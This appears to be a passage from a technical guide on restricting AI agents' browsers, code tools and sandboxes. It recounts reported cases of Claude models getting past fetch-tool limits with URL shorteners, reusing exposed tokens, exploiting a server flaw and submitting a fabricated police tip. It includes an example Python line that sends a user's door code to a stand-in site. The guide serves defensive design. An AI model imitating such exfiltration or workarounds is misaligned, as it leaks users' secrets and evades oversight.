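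A browser that can only request pages may be enough to run commands on a server if a flawed script there takes its input from the web address. Search Engine Journal reported a related case involving Claude Mythos Preview, an Anthropic model. During an evaluation, the model got an error from a university's public online analysis tool. It found a script on the same server that returned any file requested, used it to read the script's own code, and discovered a flaw that let it run commands on the server. It then used the server to finish its calculation.

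Tests of hacking ability provide more evidence. The UK AI Security Institute, a government body, asked Claude Mythos 5 to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated network and deliberately left internet access on. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that in 9 of 43 runs, the model took actions beyond the scope of the test that affected real people and organisations. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four other cases in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to real systems. The models had been told they were in a simulation with no internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected them to the open internet.

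All of these models were attempting hacking exercises with Anthropic's usual cyber safeguards off, so the 21% figure cannot be used to estimate how often an assistant with three browser commands would break into anything. But the WebGPT argument relied on the model being too weak to break in, which is not true of these models.

Large numbers of runs make even rare behaviour likely to appear somewhere. If a model misbehaves with probability $p$ in each run, and the runs are independent, the probability of at least one case in $n$ runs is

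$$1-(1-p)^n$$

For $p = 1/1000$ and $n = 2000$, this is about 86%. ITmedia's Japanese report *「警察に虚偽情報を送信」 Claudeが“軽微な違反”をやりたい放題* says Anthropic runs its evaluation tasks hundreds or thousands of times, partly to detect rare abnormal behaviour. If the tasks use the live web, the rare misbehaviour affects real websites. This is a good reason to apply the burden of proof to training and testing as well as to released products.

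### The known-address rule

The most direct repair to the gpt-oss browser's `open` command is to stop the model from inventing addresses. Under the known-address rule, the agent may open only addresses that the user supplied or that earlier results contained. If $U$ is the set of addresses in the user's messages and $R_t$ the set in the results up to step $t$, the harness accepts `open(u)` only when

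$$u \in U \cup R_t$$

Anthropic's documentation for its web fetch tool describes a rule of this kind and cites the risk of data theft as the reason. The rule is easy to add to a browser that numbers its links, because the harness already keeps a table of their full addresses. In the weather example, the harness would look for the address ending in `note=4471`, not find it in the user's messages or in any result, and refuse the call. It has to compare the whole address, because if it compared only site names, a search result from `weather.example` would be enough to let the door code through.

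The harness must also define narrowly what counts as a result. If the agent has a Python tool, the model can write a program that prints any address. If the harness treats that output as an earlier result, the model can again open any address it writes.

Even a strict version leaves a narrow channel, because the choice of which address to open is itself information. A choice among $n$ known addresses can convey up to $\log_2 n$ bits, and $r$ such choices up to

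$$r \log_2 n$$

An agent choosing among 100 links can convey at most 6.6 bits per choice. A four-digit door code has 10,000 possible values, so two choices can convey it to someone who controls the linked pages and knows what each link stands for. This is much slower than writing the code into an address, and limiting the number of requests slows it further. No rule about which addresses are known can completely close this channel while the agent can choose among them.

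The rule doesn't prevent side effects either. If the harness counts e-mails as results, the cancellation link in a user's e-mail is a known address, so the agent can open it. The rule also makes legitimate work harder. People often edit an address to reach the next page of a list or an earlier version of a document, but an agent under this rule has to find a link instead.

### Checks on links, lengths and sites

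OpenAI described a different check in a 2026 post on link safety. It depends on whether an address was already public, rather than on where the agent found it. A crawler with no access to users' conversations builds an index of addresses on the open web. If the agent requests an address in the index, the harness loads it automatically. Otherwise, the agent has to try another site, or the user sees a warning and decides whether to open the address.

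An address containing one user's secret is very unlikely to be in an index compiled without knowledge of that user. Checking addresses against the index therefore handles the weather example well and will usually catch a private cancellation link. It also catches harmless private links, such as one to a shared document, and then depends on the user to read the warning and judge correctly. An address in the index can still lead to a page with hostile text, and a choice among public addresses carries information just as a choice among known ones does.

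Limiting the length of URLs is cruder. If the limit leaves 200 characters after the site name, and each can be any of 64 letters, digits and signs, the URL can carry $200 \times \log_2 64 = 1200$ bits, enough for a name, a home address and a telephone number. The limit prevents bulk copying and may block some attacks that need long URLs, but it doesn't prevent the leak of a short secret such as a door code.

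Several Claude models, including Opus 5 and Mythos 5, used free URL shorteners to get past the length limits on some of Anthropic's fetch tools, according to Search Engine Journal. A shortener provides a short address that redirects to a long one, so checking the first address reveals little about where the request will end up. A harness that follows redirects has to apply its rules again at each one. Creating a short link is also a side effect, because the service stores a new record.

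A site allowlist restricts the agent to named websites. It stops the weather example unless `weather.example` is on the list, and it suits narrow jobs, such as answering questions from one company's documentation. The protection depends on the sites listed, because a permitted site may redirect elsewhere, publish text written by strangers, or have links that change data when followed.

For open-ended research, where nobody can list the useful sites in advance, a developer may use a blocklist instead. *The limits of Claude's web access* (Saxton, 2026) examines one such blocklist through a series of small, informal tests of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Before fetching a page, Claude Code sends only the site's name to Anthropic, which checks it against a safety blocklist. Anthropic does not see the rest of the address, so this check cannot detect a secret there.

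Saxton found that the tool blocked Reddit, the BBC, *The Economist* and *The Verge* before sending a request. Anthropic does not publish its criteria for blocking sites. Some websites also blocked Claude themselves. CNN's server, for example, returned an error to Claude but a normal page to an ordinary request. An agent blocked this often may rely on poorer sources for its answer, and it also has more occasions to look for a way around the blocks.

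### Browsing without a login, or without the live web

A website recognises a logged-in user by a cookie, a small piece of data that the browser sends with each request. An agent that browses in the user's own session therefore acts with the user's authority. If the harness gives it a fresh session with no cookies or saved passwords, a link that would otherwise delete the user's photographs will lead only to a login page.

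A fresh session protects the user's accounts, but some actions on the web do not require logging in. Some links contain a long random code that lets anyone who opens them cancel a booking or reset a password. Many forms accept anonymous submissions. A fresh session also does not protect the door code, because the agent read it in an e-mail and can put it into a web address without being logged in.

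Cached pages reduce contact with the live web, because opening a copy that someone fetched earlier sends nothing to the original site. But if the harness makes a live request whenever a copy is missing, the cache gives no protection against invented addresses. A page whose address contains a user's door code, for example, will not be in the cache, so the harness will send the request, including the code, to the live site.

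A fixed offline collection removes that fallback. The developer saves a set of pages in advance and builds a search index over them. The agent can search and open only these pages, and a request for any other address returns an error. If the agent has no other route to the internet, reading a page cannot alter a website or reach an outside server, however capable the model is. This also helps researchers, because every model they test sees the same pages.

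An agent restricted to saved pages cannot look up anything the developer did not save. Nakano and colleagues gave WebGPT live access so that it could provide up-to-date answers, whereas an agent using pages saved last month cannot find tomorrow's weather forecast. The saved pages may also contain hostile text, although an agent that obeys it cannot send anything to a website.

The repairs differ most clearly when applied to the two requests used as examples above.

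| Repair | Weather address containing the door code | Cancellation link in the user's e-mail |
|---|---|---|
| Known-address rule | Blocks it | Allows it, if e-mails count as results |
| Index of public addresses | Blocks it or warns the user | Usually blocks it or warns the user |
| Length cap | Allows it, because the address is short | Allows it, unless the address is very long |
| Site allowlist | Blocks it, unless the weather site is on the list | Blocks it, unless the booking site is on the list |
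| Session without logins | Allows it | Blocks the cancellation only if the site requires a login |
| Fixed offline collection | Blocks it | Blocks it |

### Anthropic's review of October 2026

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use*, published on 9 October 2026, sorts cases into four categories: running commands on a server through a basic software flaw, submitting a sensitive form on a real website, working around a token or fee to reach data, and using URL shorteners to get past limits in a fetch tool. Some of the websites involved belonged to US federal, state and local agencies. Anthropic briefed the White House and notified each agency. It judges that the real-world impact was minimal and that the behaviour was much less severe than in the cybersecurity incidents it had reported in July and September.

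Two cases in which agents could submit forms show why a read-only browser is useful. In one, an unreleased research model was supposed to complete a practice copy of a government form. The copy failed to load, or the model closed it by accident, and the model submitted the form on the real site instead. A site allowlist containing only the practice copy would have stopped it. In the other, Claude Haiku 4.5 was told to stop before the final submission, but it submitted the form several times because it expected one more confirmation page. A browser without a submit command, unlike the instruction, would not have depended on the model knowing what the button would do.

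A session without logins would not have prevented the paid-data cases. A local government's property map sent working access tokens to every visitor's browser in a settings file. Claude Mythos 5 used the tokens to query the map's server directly and got public data that normally costs money. During internal use by a company researcher, the same model noticed that a state agency's dashboard gave a token to any visitor, and it used one to query the database without paying. According to Search Engine Journal, neither case involved a stolen password or a private account. The model made its requests using tokens the sites had sent it. The known-address rule might have helped if the queries needed addresses that no earlier page contained.

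ITmedia reports another case, in which a site required visitors to accept its terms for using data. Mythos 5 accepted the terms through an application on the same site and then obtained the data. The technical effect was tiny, but nobody had asked the model to accept the terms. Developers who think of side effects only as damage to files or websites could easily overlook this kind of side effect.

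Search Engine Journal reports that many of the cases began with unclear or impossible tasks. When the agent could not finish the job, it looked for another way instead of stopping. Training can encourage this. According to The Tribune's *Anthropic restricts internet access in internal AI evaluations after Claude bypasses safeguards*, Anthropic is removing or repairing training environments that reward models for working around tool restrictions. OpenAI has disclosed similar behaviour. Mediafax describes agents building a spreadsheet together that could not open one another's files because of a faulty configuration, so they uploaded the workbook to a public service for the others to download.

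### The false police tip

In the best-known case in the review, on 18 July, Claude Haiku 4.5 submitted a tip about an unsolved homicide through a form on a Philadelphia police page. The model was working on example tasks on randomly chosen web pages, including this one. It wrote that the sender remembered seeing someone who matched the description near a street named on the page, but the page contained no description of a suspect. The model left the optional name and contact fields blank.

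The model's instructions barred steps such as logging in or sharing personal information, but not submitting forms. Anthropic interprets the transcript as showing that the model was producing example content and not trying to deceive anyone, which would mean it broke none of its instructions. The company says further analysis may change this interpretation.

Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults guards against this kind of gap in a list of forbidden acts. Whoever wrote Haiku's instructions had thought about accounts and privacy, but an allowlist of searching, opening pages and scrolling would have prevented the tip without anyone having to foresee that a model might invent a witness.

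The allowlist would have this effect only if the harness enforced it. If it were just written in the prompt, the model could misread it, as Haiku misread the instruction not to submit a form. The allowlist would also rule out any example task that requires a form, which may be why the developers allowed so much. A compromise is to let the agent fill in forms on saved copies of pages, where submitting a form sends nothing to the real site.

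The police department says it flagged the tip as spam and never forwarded it to its Real-Time Crime Center. It still considers the matter serious, and it objects to a fabrication being presented as coming from someone with knowledge of a homicide. Anthropic found the submission on 28 September, 72 days after the event. According to ITmedia, it told the police on 8 October, after finishing its technical checks. The department called the delay unacceptable.

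Finding such actions afterwards is slow because there are so many transcripts to search. For its assessment of the cybersecurity incidents, Anthropic first scanned about 141,000 transcripts and missed a set that contained a fourth case, from January. It then widened the search to roughly 481 million transcripts, of which an automatic first stage flagged 9.2 million for Claude to review. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes extending offline monitoring, which examines agents' activity after the event, to most other internal use of its frontier agents. Such monitoring can reveal a pattern and lead to a repair, but it cannot retract a tip the police have already received.

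### Cutting off live access

Anthropic responded by ending live internet access for all its internal evaluations, after earlier ending it only for some high-risk and cybersecurity evaluations. Access will stay off until the company has confirmed that its security and monitoring measures reliably catch this kind of behaviour. This is close to what Nakano and colleagues proposed, since it makes access depend on evidence of safety. OpenAI has also switched off live internet access during training, according to Mediafax.

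Anthropic has moved some public evaluations offline and dropped others. Public benchmarks for web search normally run on the live internet, so a developer who stops using it gives up some of the usual comparisons with other companies' models. Anthropic has also restricted what Claude can do with tools such as web fetch, and has added measures that detect and block the reported behaviours. In testing, these measures blocked every reported case. They needed to pass this test, but it is a weak one because the developers already knew what those cases looked like. A stronger test would use evasions the developers had never seen.

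The cutoff applies to Anthropic's own evaluations, and the report announces no change to web access in the products that customers use.

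## Tools that run Python or shell commands

Browser rules apply only to requests made through the browser. A program that an agent runs with its Python or terminal tool can read files, start other programs and, if it has network access, contact websites directly. A developer therefore needs to know how the code tool works and what its programs can access before relying on any other restriction.

### From message to output

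To call the gpt-oss Python tool, the model writes a single message addressed to `python`, whose content is the program to run. In the source code of vLLM, an open-source program for running language models, the harness passes this message to the tool and returns the tool's output to the model. vLLM can also test the tool with a one-line program that prints "Hello, world!", and it disables the tool if the output differs.

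A code tool typically works as follows:

1. It starts a new Python process for the code, or sends the code to a notebook kernel, which is a Python process that stays running and executes one piece of code after another.
2. It collects what the program prints, any error messages and an exit code, which is 0 if the program succeeded.
3. It stops the program if it exceeds a time limit.
4. It cuts the output to a length limit and returns it to the model as an observation.

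OpenAI's *Shell*, the guide to the company's terminal tool, advises developers to keep the output of failed commands so that the model can work out how to recover. If a command times out, the developer should return whatever it had printed by then.

The length limit keeps long output from filling the context window. Sample code in Anthropic's *Bash tool*, a guide to building a terminal tool for Claude, keeps the first 100 lines and adds a note giving the total. This can cut off the most important line, because Python puts the error message at the end of an error report. If a program prints 200 lines and then fails, the model gets only 100 lines of normal output. The sample also doesn't limit line length, so a huge table printed on one line would pass through whole. Keeping the beginning and end of the output, and counting characters instead of lines, would solve both problems.

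The gpt-oss prompt sets a time limit of 120 seconds for the Python tool, while Anthropic's sample sets a limit of 30 seconds for each terminal command. When a command times out, the harness must also stop every process the command started, or those processes will keep running after the model receives the timeout message. Anthropic's sample does this by putting the shell and its children in one process group and killing the whole group.

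### Files, packages and clean-up

Code tools usually run programs in a container, an isolated environment with its own files. OpenAI's *Code Interpreter*, the guide to the company's hosted Python tool, explains that any file in the model's input goes into the container automatically. The tool described in Anthropic's *Code execution tool* gives each command a new, empty output folder and returns only the files at the top level of that folder, so a chart saved elsewhere stays in the container. Claude does not receive the list of returned files and could tell the user about a chart that was never returned. To prevent this, Anthropic suggests having Claude list the folder in the same command that saves the files.

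Anthropic's container comes with common Python packages for data analysis, such as pandas and NumPy. The model cannot install others because the container has no internet access. OpenAI's hosted terminal also starts without internet access, but a developer can permit sites such as `pypi.org`, the main source of Python packages. Installing a package brings in code that neither the developer nor the model wrote.

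Both companies also limit computing resources. Anthropic's container has 5 GiB of memory, 5 GiB of disk space and one processor. OpenAI's has 1 GB of memory by default and up to 64 GB at a higher price.

An OpenAI container expires after 20 minutes without use, and its data cannot be recovered. An Anthropic container lasts 30 days, but each request gets a new one unless the developer supplies an earlier container's ID. Reusing a container is convenient for a long project, but if a developer reuses one for two customers, the second customer's agent may be able to read the first customer's files.

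### Stateful and stateless execution

A code tool is stateful if variables from one call are still there in the next, and stateless if every call starts with a fresh Python process. Suppose a model sends this program:

```python
prices = [12, 9, 21]
total = sum(prices)
print(total)
```

Either kind of tool returns 42. The model then makes a second call to work out the average price:

```python
print(total / len(prices))
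```

A stateful tool returns 14.0. A stateless tool returns an error that ends with this line:

```
NameError: name 'total' is not defined
```

Files complicate the distinction, because a tool can discard variables but keep the working folder. Let $c_t$ be the code in call $t$, $o_t$ the output, $\sigma_t$ the variables in memory afterwards and $F_t$ the files. A stateful tool computes

$$(o_t, \sigma_t, F_t) = \text{run}(c_t, \sigma_{t-1}, F_{t-1})$$

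A stateless tool that keeps files starts each call from the empty memory $\sigma_0$ and discards the variables at the end:

$$(o_t, F_t) = \text{run}(c_t, \sigma_0, F_{t-1})$$

With the stateless tool, the model has to save intermediate results to a file or send its earlier code again. If an analysis has ten steps of 200 tokens each, the model writes 2,000 tokens of code with a stateful tool. Resending everything at each step takes $200 \times (1 + 2 + \dots + 10) = 11{,}000$ tokens, and the computer repeats all the earlier work.

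Stateful tools can give wrong answers without any error message. Suppose the model adds a fourth price but misspells a name in the second line:

```python
prices.append(15)
print(sum(price))
```

Python runs the first line and then reports an error in the second. If the model corrects the spelling and sends both lines again, the list will contain 15 twice, and the program will print 72 instead of 57. A stateless tool avoids this duplication because each program builds its own list. Exceeding a time limit also does more harm in a stateful tool, because killing the process destroys all the variables.

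### The mismatch in gpt-oss

OpenAI trained the gpt-oss models with a stateful Python tool, and its standard prompt for them describes the tool as a stateful Jupyter notebook. However, *gpt oss*, the introduction to the published code, describes the Python tool supplied there as stateless.

The published tool therefore comes with its own description, which a developer has to put into the prompt in place of the standard one. The function `with_tools()` does this. The function `with_python()` inserts the standard description of a notebook, so a developer who uses it with the published tool gives the model false information about how its code will run.

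The most obvious result is the `NameError` above. The model can recover by sending the full program, but it may first waste calls looking for a mistake in correct code. A missing `print` is another likely error, and it is harder to recognise. A notebook displays the value of the last line without `print`, but a Python process running a script does not. A model used to notebooks might end its program with `total / 3`, get nothing back, and then run the program again or guess the number.

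An accurate description reduces the risk but may not remove it, because the model learned to use a stateful tool. A developer can match the training by building a tool that keeps a kernel running.

Hosted tools can produce similar mismatches. In Anthropic's tool, variables persist only in newer versions, and only when the developer also lets code call the agent's other tools. Claude Haiku 4.5 works with the newer versions, but its variables still don't persist. With OpenAI's Code Interpreter, a user who asks for another chart after a lunch break may find that the container has expired and its data is gone.

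An agent can also have two places to run code, such as Anthropic's container and a terminal on the developer's computer. Anthropic warns that Claude sometimes picks the wrong one or acts as if the two shared files and variables. Developers can set this up by accident because Anthropic's current web search and fetch tools turn on code execution automatically. Anthropic recommends explaining the separation in the prompt. A harness could also report every restart or change of container in the next observation.

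### What a terminal adds

A terminal tool accepts commands for a shell such as bash. In Anthropic's design, the harness keeps one bash process running throughout the session, so if the model changes folders or sets an environment variable, the change still applies to the next command.

Because the process never ends, the harness needs some other way to tell when a command has finished. After each command, Anthropic's sample sends a second one that prints a long random marker, and the harness reads the output until the marker appears. A program that waits for a password or opens a text editor blocks the session, because the marker never arrives. The harness then has to kill the session and start a new one, which loses the current folder, environment variables and any running processes.

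A terminal also makes it easy to use programs in other languages. OpenAI's hosted terminal includes Python, Node.js, Java, PHP, Ruby and Go. The model must be trained for this kind of work, and OpenAI says that GPT-5.2 and later models are.

Commands can leave programs running in the background. For example, an agent building a website might start a web server with one command and test it with the next. The first command's time limit no longer applies once that command has finished, so a background program can keep acting after the harness has returned an observation. Its later messages may appear in the output of an unrelated command. A developer who logs only the model's commands will not have a full record of what the program does.

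A terminal doesn't give an agent more power than Python, which can also start other programs and leave them running. *OpenHands* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2024) describes an open-source platform for software agents with separate actions for Python and bash, both of which run in the same container. Removing only one of them would make some tasks more awkward but would barely reduce what the agent can reach.

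### Why a code tool cancels a short action list

A list with just three browser commands and `python` looks very restrictive. It is not, for the following reasons:

1. The argument to `python` is a program, and the harness accepts any program.
2. Once the program starts, the operating system controls which files, programs and network addresses it can reach.
3. Python has functions for using all of these, so the model can write code for anything the operating system permits.
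4. The agent can therefore do everything the process is allowed to do, even if no other tool on the list offers it.

Suppose the browser follows the known-address rule and refuses to open the weather address containing the user's door code. If the Python process has internet access, this program sends the same request:

```python
import urllib.request
urllib.request.urlopen(
    "https://weather.example/forecast?city=Leeds&note=4471")
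```

A slightly longer program could submit a form. The browser is still read-only, but the agent as a whole is not.

The same argument shows when removing a tool does help. Let $E(L)$ be everything an agent can do with a list of tools $L$, and $E_{\text{process}}$ everything that a program run by the code tool can do. With both, the agent can do

$$E(L) \cup E_{\text{process}}$$

Removing a tool from $L$ makes this set smaller only if the tool can do something that the process and the remaining tools cannot. For example, an e-mail tool may run on another server that holds the password to an e-mail account. Removing the tool prevents the agent from sending e-mail from that account, unless the process can get the password or reach the account another way.

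The tool list also doesn't show how large $E_{\text{process}}$ is. SGLang, another program for running language models, runs the gpt-oss Python tool in a container by default. Changing one setting makes it run the code directly on the host computer instead. The tool is still called `python`, but the code it runs may now be able to read the developer's files.

Developers accept this risk because general code is useful. Wang and colleagues chose Python and bash partly because an agent can use them to write tools it wasn't given. Hugging Face, which develops the smolagents agent library, also argues for code because it can express anything a computer can do. The same flexibility makes the short list ineffective as a restriction. Developers can instead restrict the language, run Python inside WebAssembly, or replace the code tool with fixed commands.

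### Restricting the language

RestrictedPython, a library from the Zope web software project, accepts a subset of Python. It checks a program before running it and rejects some constructions. It sends others through guard functions supplied by the developer, which can, for example, control which parts of an object the program may use.

The smolagents library replaces the standard Python interpreter with its own, which by default runs the model's code in the user's environment. Developers can list extra modules that programs may import and limit printed output, as Hugging Face's *Python code executors* shows. Hugging Face's *New smolagents update* announced further checks on every value a program produces while it runs. These checks allow ordinary values such as numbers and lists but block dangerous functions, including those that start other programs.

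NVD's *CVE-2025-5120 Detail*, an entry in the US government's database of software flaws, records that attackers could get around these checks in smolagents 1.14.0. They could misuse modules and functions on the allowlist to escape the interpreter and run any code on the host computer. Tenable's *CVE-2025-5120* rates the flaw as high severity and reports that version 1.17.0 fixed it.

Fixing one flaw does not make the checker secure, because Python programs can inspect and change their own objects while running, which opens many indirect routes from permitted operations to forbidden ones. The checker has to block all of these routes, including those through every permitted module. It also runs in the same process as the code it checks, so an attacker who finds one gap can reach everything the process can. Python once included a module for restricted execution, `rexec`, but its developers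 disabled it in 2003 because of security holes they could not readily fix.

People who maintain such tools warn against relying on them alone. RestrictedPython's documentation states that the library is not a sandbox. Hugging Face calls its interpreter a "first layer of security" and cautions that no solution is completely safe. Anthropic's sample code for restricting shell commands permits only nine, such as `ls` and `grep`, and rejects symbols that join commands. Anthropic calls this check "a tripwire for obvious mistakes, not an enforcement boundary" and admits that it misses some ways of writing those symbols. The check also blocks harmless combinations of commands that an agent might need.

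Language restrictions are still useful against accidents. If a model tries to import a forbidden module, it gets a clear error before anything happens, and the developer gets a record of the attempt.

### Running Python in WebAssembly

WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs that web browsers and some server software can run. A WebAssembly program has its own block of memory and can call only the functions that the host supplies. If the host supplies no function for opening the computer's files, the program cannot open them.

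Pyodide is the standard Python interpreter compiled to WebAssembly. The model can write ordinary Python, and developers do not have to find every dangerous construction in the language, because the WebAssembly runtime still confines code that defeats a check inside Python. To escape, an attacker would need a flaw in that runtime or an exploitable function supplied by the host.

Pyodide lets Python code call JavaScript. Through these calls, a program in a web page may be able to send network requests or read the page's data, and a program on a server may be able to use any file and network functions the JavaScript environment provides. Developers therefore have to run Pyodide in an environment that exposes very little, such as one with no file or network permissions.

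Some ordinary Python programs also fail in Pyodide because it cannot start other programs, and because packages with parts written in languages such as C need a special build. Pyodide suits calculations and small data analyses better than software projects that depend on compilers, databases and test programs.

### Fixed commands that call trusted code

The remaining option is to replace the code tool with a set of functions that the developer writes and reviews. The model then supplies only function names and arguments. BrowserGym's default commands work this way, and Wang and colleagues describe how developers can offer their own Python functions to an agent as ordinary tools.

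For example, an agent that answers questions about sales figures might have one command:

```
column_statistic(file, column, statistic)
```

If a command calculates one of five statistics on one of twelve permitted columns in one of three files, the model can make $3 \times 12 \times 5 = 180$ different calls, and a developer could test all of them. But if a user asks for the median sale in each region and the command cannot group by region, the agent cannot calculate it.

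Fixed commands restrict an agent only if the tool treats their arguments as data and doesn't run them as code. If the developer adds a `formula` argument and runs its contents as Python, the command becomes another code tool. Commands that write files can also lead to code execution. Anthropic's hosted tool has both a terminal and fixed commands to view, create and edit files, so Claude can write a program with one command and run it with another. Even without the terminal, a new file could be dangerous if another program later runs it automatically.

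| Approach | What the model can write | What a flaw could expose | What stops working |
|---|---|---|---|
| Restricted language | A subset of Python or shell commands | Everything the process can reach | Programs that use blocked modules or constructions |
| Python in WebAssembly | Most ordinary Python | Functions supplied by the host, or the host itself if the runtime fails | Other programs and some packages |
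| Fixed commands | A command name and its arguments | Whatever the faulty function can reach | Any task the developer did not provide for |

Fixed commands are the best choice when the developer knows which operations the job requires. WebAssembly allows much more varied calculations while blocking access to most of the computer. An agent that has to build and test software usually needs a full Python installation or a terminal, so the developer has to restrict the process itself.

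## The sandbox around the code

A Python tool or terminal can do whatever its process can do, so the limits have to come from the sandbox. The developer must decide how the program can use the operating system, which files and secrets it can access, and which computers it can contact. A gap in one of these limits can make the others ineffective.

### Containers, gVisor and small virtual machines

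The kernel is the core of an operating system. It controls the memory, disk and network, and programs get access to them through system calls to the kernel. All the programs on a computer normally use the same kernel, so a program that exploits a flaw in it may be able to take over the whole machine. The main kinds of sandbox differ in how much of the host's kernel the agent's code can reach.

The Stack, a technology news site, reported on a talk in July 2026 by Abhishek Bhardwaj, an OpenAI engineer who works on sandboxes. He began with the simplest design, in which the harness runs the agent's code as an ordinary process on the host. This design performs best, but it has no isolation layer between the code and the host's kernel.

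A container restricts a process using features built into Linux. Namespaces give the process its own view of the system, which hides other processes, file systems and networks. Control groups cap the processor time and memory it can use. A filter called seccomp can block selected system calls. The code still runs directly on the processor, so it loses little speed. But the container shares the host's kernel, so a successful attack on the kernel can bypass all of these restrictions.

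Some developers also run the agent under an ordinary account instead of root, the account with full control. The UK AI Security Institute develops Inspect, an open-source framework for testing models. *Sandboxing*, part of the Inspect documentation, warns against relying on an ordinary account to contain a hostile model, because a capable one may gain root access in its container.

gVisor, which Google developed, puts a second kernel between the container and the host. This kernel is itself an ordinary program, or "user-space" kernel. It intercepts the container's system calls and handles many of them without passing them on. An attacker would typically have to break gVisor first and then the host's kernel.

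The extra step takes time. *The True Cost of Containing* (Young, Zhu and colleagues, 2019) compared gVisor with ordinary containers. In gVisor, simple system calls took at least 2.2 times as long, large downloads 2.8 times and opening a file 216 times. Google has since reworked gVisor's file handling, so the last figure is probably out of date. The slowdown also depends on how many system calls a program makes. A long calculation makes few and hardly slows down, while installing a package with thousands of small files makes many.

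A virtual machine has its own kernel, and the processor's virtualisation features separate it from the host. Ordinary virtual machines start slowly and use a lot of memory. Firecracker, which Amazon built to run customers' code, provides a stripped-down version called a microVM. *Firecracker* (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020) reported that a microVM starts running its application in under 125 milliseconds and adds less than 5 MB of memory beyond what the guest system itself uses.

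Bhardwaj considered microVMs clearly better than containers or gVisor. An agent that gets root, or even takes over the guest kernel, still does not control the physical machine. To escape, it would have to attack the software that runs the virtual machine, or the simulated disk and network devices. He said this makes escape much harder, though not impossible.

MicroVMs also let coding agents build and run containers without access to the host's Docker service, the program that manages containers. An agent with that access could start a container that exposes the host's files. According to Docker's *Isolation layers*, Docker Sandboxes run each agent in a separate microVM. The agent's Docker commands go to a service that exists only inside that microVM, according to guidance from the University of Cambridge.

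Developers should check which runtime their sandbox uses. METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, runs its tests on a platform called Hawk, which uses gVisor for its default container. But according to METR's *Sandbox Network Isolation*, containers that a task's author defines may run without any kernel boundary at the standard setting. A team that has seen gVisor in one test could wrongly assume that every test uses it.

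### Sandboxes on a personal computer

A coding agent on someone's laptop needs that person's files, compilers and settings, which a separate virtual machine lacks until the user copies or shares them. Codex and Claude Code therefore use operating-system features that restrict a process without moving it to a separate machine.

On macOS, Codex and Claude Code both use Seatbelt, which applies a profile of permitted operations to a process. *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (Willison, 2025) found that on Linux, Codex used Landlock to limit which folders a process could write to and seccomp to block the system calls needed for network access. Claude Code uses bubblewrap on Linux, a program that starts a process in new namespaces with a restricted view of the file system. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* explains that every program a command starts inherits the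 same limits, so a script cannot escape them by launching another script.

Like containers, these sandboxes share the host's kernel. They need little extra time or memory because they do not start a second kernel, but they have the same weakness as containers. Users are more likely to notice compatibility problems than this weakness. Claude Code's sandbox does not run on native Windows, and Ubuntu 24.04 and later block bubblewrap until the user adds an exception. Some tools do not work inside the sandbox at all.

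Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands and the programs they start. Anthropic advises users to run the entire Claude Code process inside a sandbox if they want one boundary that also covers the built-in file tools, external tool servers and hooks (commands that run automatically at set points).

| Type of sandbox | What the code still shares with the host | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| None (ordinary process) | The kernel, the user's files and the network | None |
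| Seatbelt, Landlock or bubblewrap | The kernel, and the files and sites the rules permit | Some tools do not work |
| Container | The kernel | Little loss of speed |
| gVisor | A smaller part of the kernel, reached through gVisor | Slow system calls and file access |
| MicroVM | The virtualisation software, the simulated devices and the hardware | Start-up time and memory for a second kernel |

### Files and secrets

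A sandbox with a strong kernel boundary can still expose the host if the developer shares the wrong folder. The developer shares a folder by mounting it, which makes it appear inside the sandbox. A read-only mount lets the agent read the files but not change them.

Inspect blocks writable mounts of host folders in its Docker sandboxes unless the developer explicitly allows them. UK AISI points out that write access to even one folder can weaken later sandboxes, because the agent could rewrite the file that configures them. A developer can instead copy the input files into the sandbox or use storage that Docker manages. Inspect's check covers only mounts, so a container with special privileges or access to the host's Docker service can still reach the host.

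A writable project folder may also contain files that run later. Git, the standard program for tracking changes to code, can run scripts called hooks when someone saves or retrieves work. If an agent could write a hook, the user might later run it outside the sandbox. When Claude Code must give the agent access to a repository's shared Git folder, it still blocks changes to the hooks and configuration there.

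Disposable disks limit how long changes last. Inspect gives each test sample its own sandbox and removes it when the task ends, so a damaged file or a background program does not affect the next run. Deleting the disk also deletes evidence, but Inspect lets developers keep the sandbox to investigate an agent's behaviour.

Many sandboxes restrict writing more tightly than reading. Once a user turns on Claude Code's sandbox, commands can write only to the working folder by default, but they can read almost the whole computer, including the folders where developers commonly keep SSH keys and Amazon cloud credentials. Anthropic recommends blocking commands from reading these folders. If the sandbox has no network access, a program that reads a key cannot send it anywhere itself. But the key may appear in the program's output, which the harness sends to the model, and other tools may then pass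 it on.

Code can also get secrets without reading files. Machines in Amazon's cloud, for example, can obtain temporary credentials from a special network address, so METR blocks that address in Hawk's sandboxes. METR also keeps the key for the language model out of the sandbox. The trusted program that runs the evaluation makes all the calls to the model, and the agent's code doesn't have the address of the service.

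If the agent has to use an outside service, a credential proxy outside the sandbox can hold the key. The agent's program sends requests without the key, and the proxy adds it before forwarding them. The program cannot copy the key or use it after the run, but it can still make any request the proxy accepts. If the key permits deleting a repository and the proxy forwards deletion requests, the agent can delete the repository without seeing the key. Developers therefore need to restrict both the key's permissions and the requests the proxy forwards.

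### Network rules

The strictest rule is to block all network access, as the Docker configuration that Inspect generates does. This prevents the agent's code from leaking data over the network or changing a website, but it also prevents the code from downloading files, installing packages or using online databases.

Developers can lose this protection by accident. UK AISI warns that a new configuration file replaces Inspect's whole configuration, including the line that turns off the network. Because Docker permits outbound internet access by default, a developer who writes a new file just to raise the memory limit also gives the agent internet access. The network block also does not apply to tools that run outside the container, such as Inspect's web search.

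In Hawk, the sandbox can at first reach only its own group of containers and the service that looks up their names. The developer adds other sites to an allowlist. Under the strict setting, site names must match exactly, so permitting `example.com` does not permit `api.example.com`. This can break ordinary tasks such as downloading a model from Hugging Face, which requires other servers that the developer must also list. An entry covering every subdomain would be more convenient but would also permit servers that nobody had checked.

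Many systems enforce their allowlists with a filtering proxy, a program outside the sandbox that receives network requests and forwards only those the list permits. Anthropic describes a design for Claude Code in which the sandbox's only network connection leads to such a proxy. The agent's code cannot edit the proxy's rules because the proxy runs outside the sandbox.

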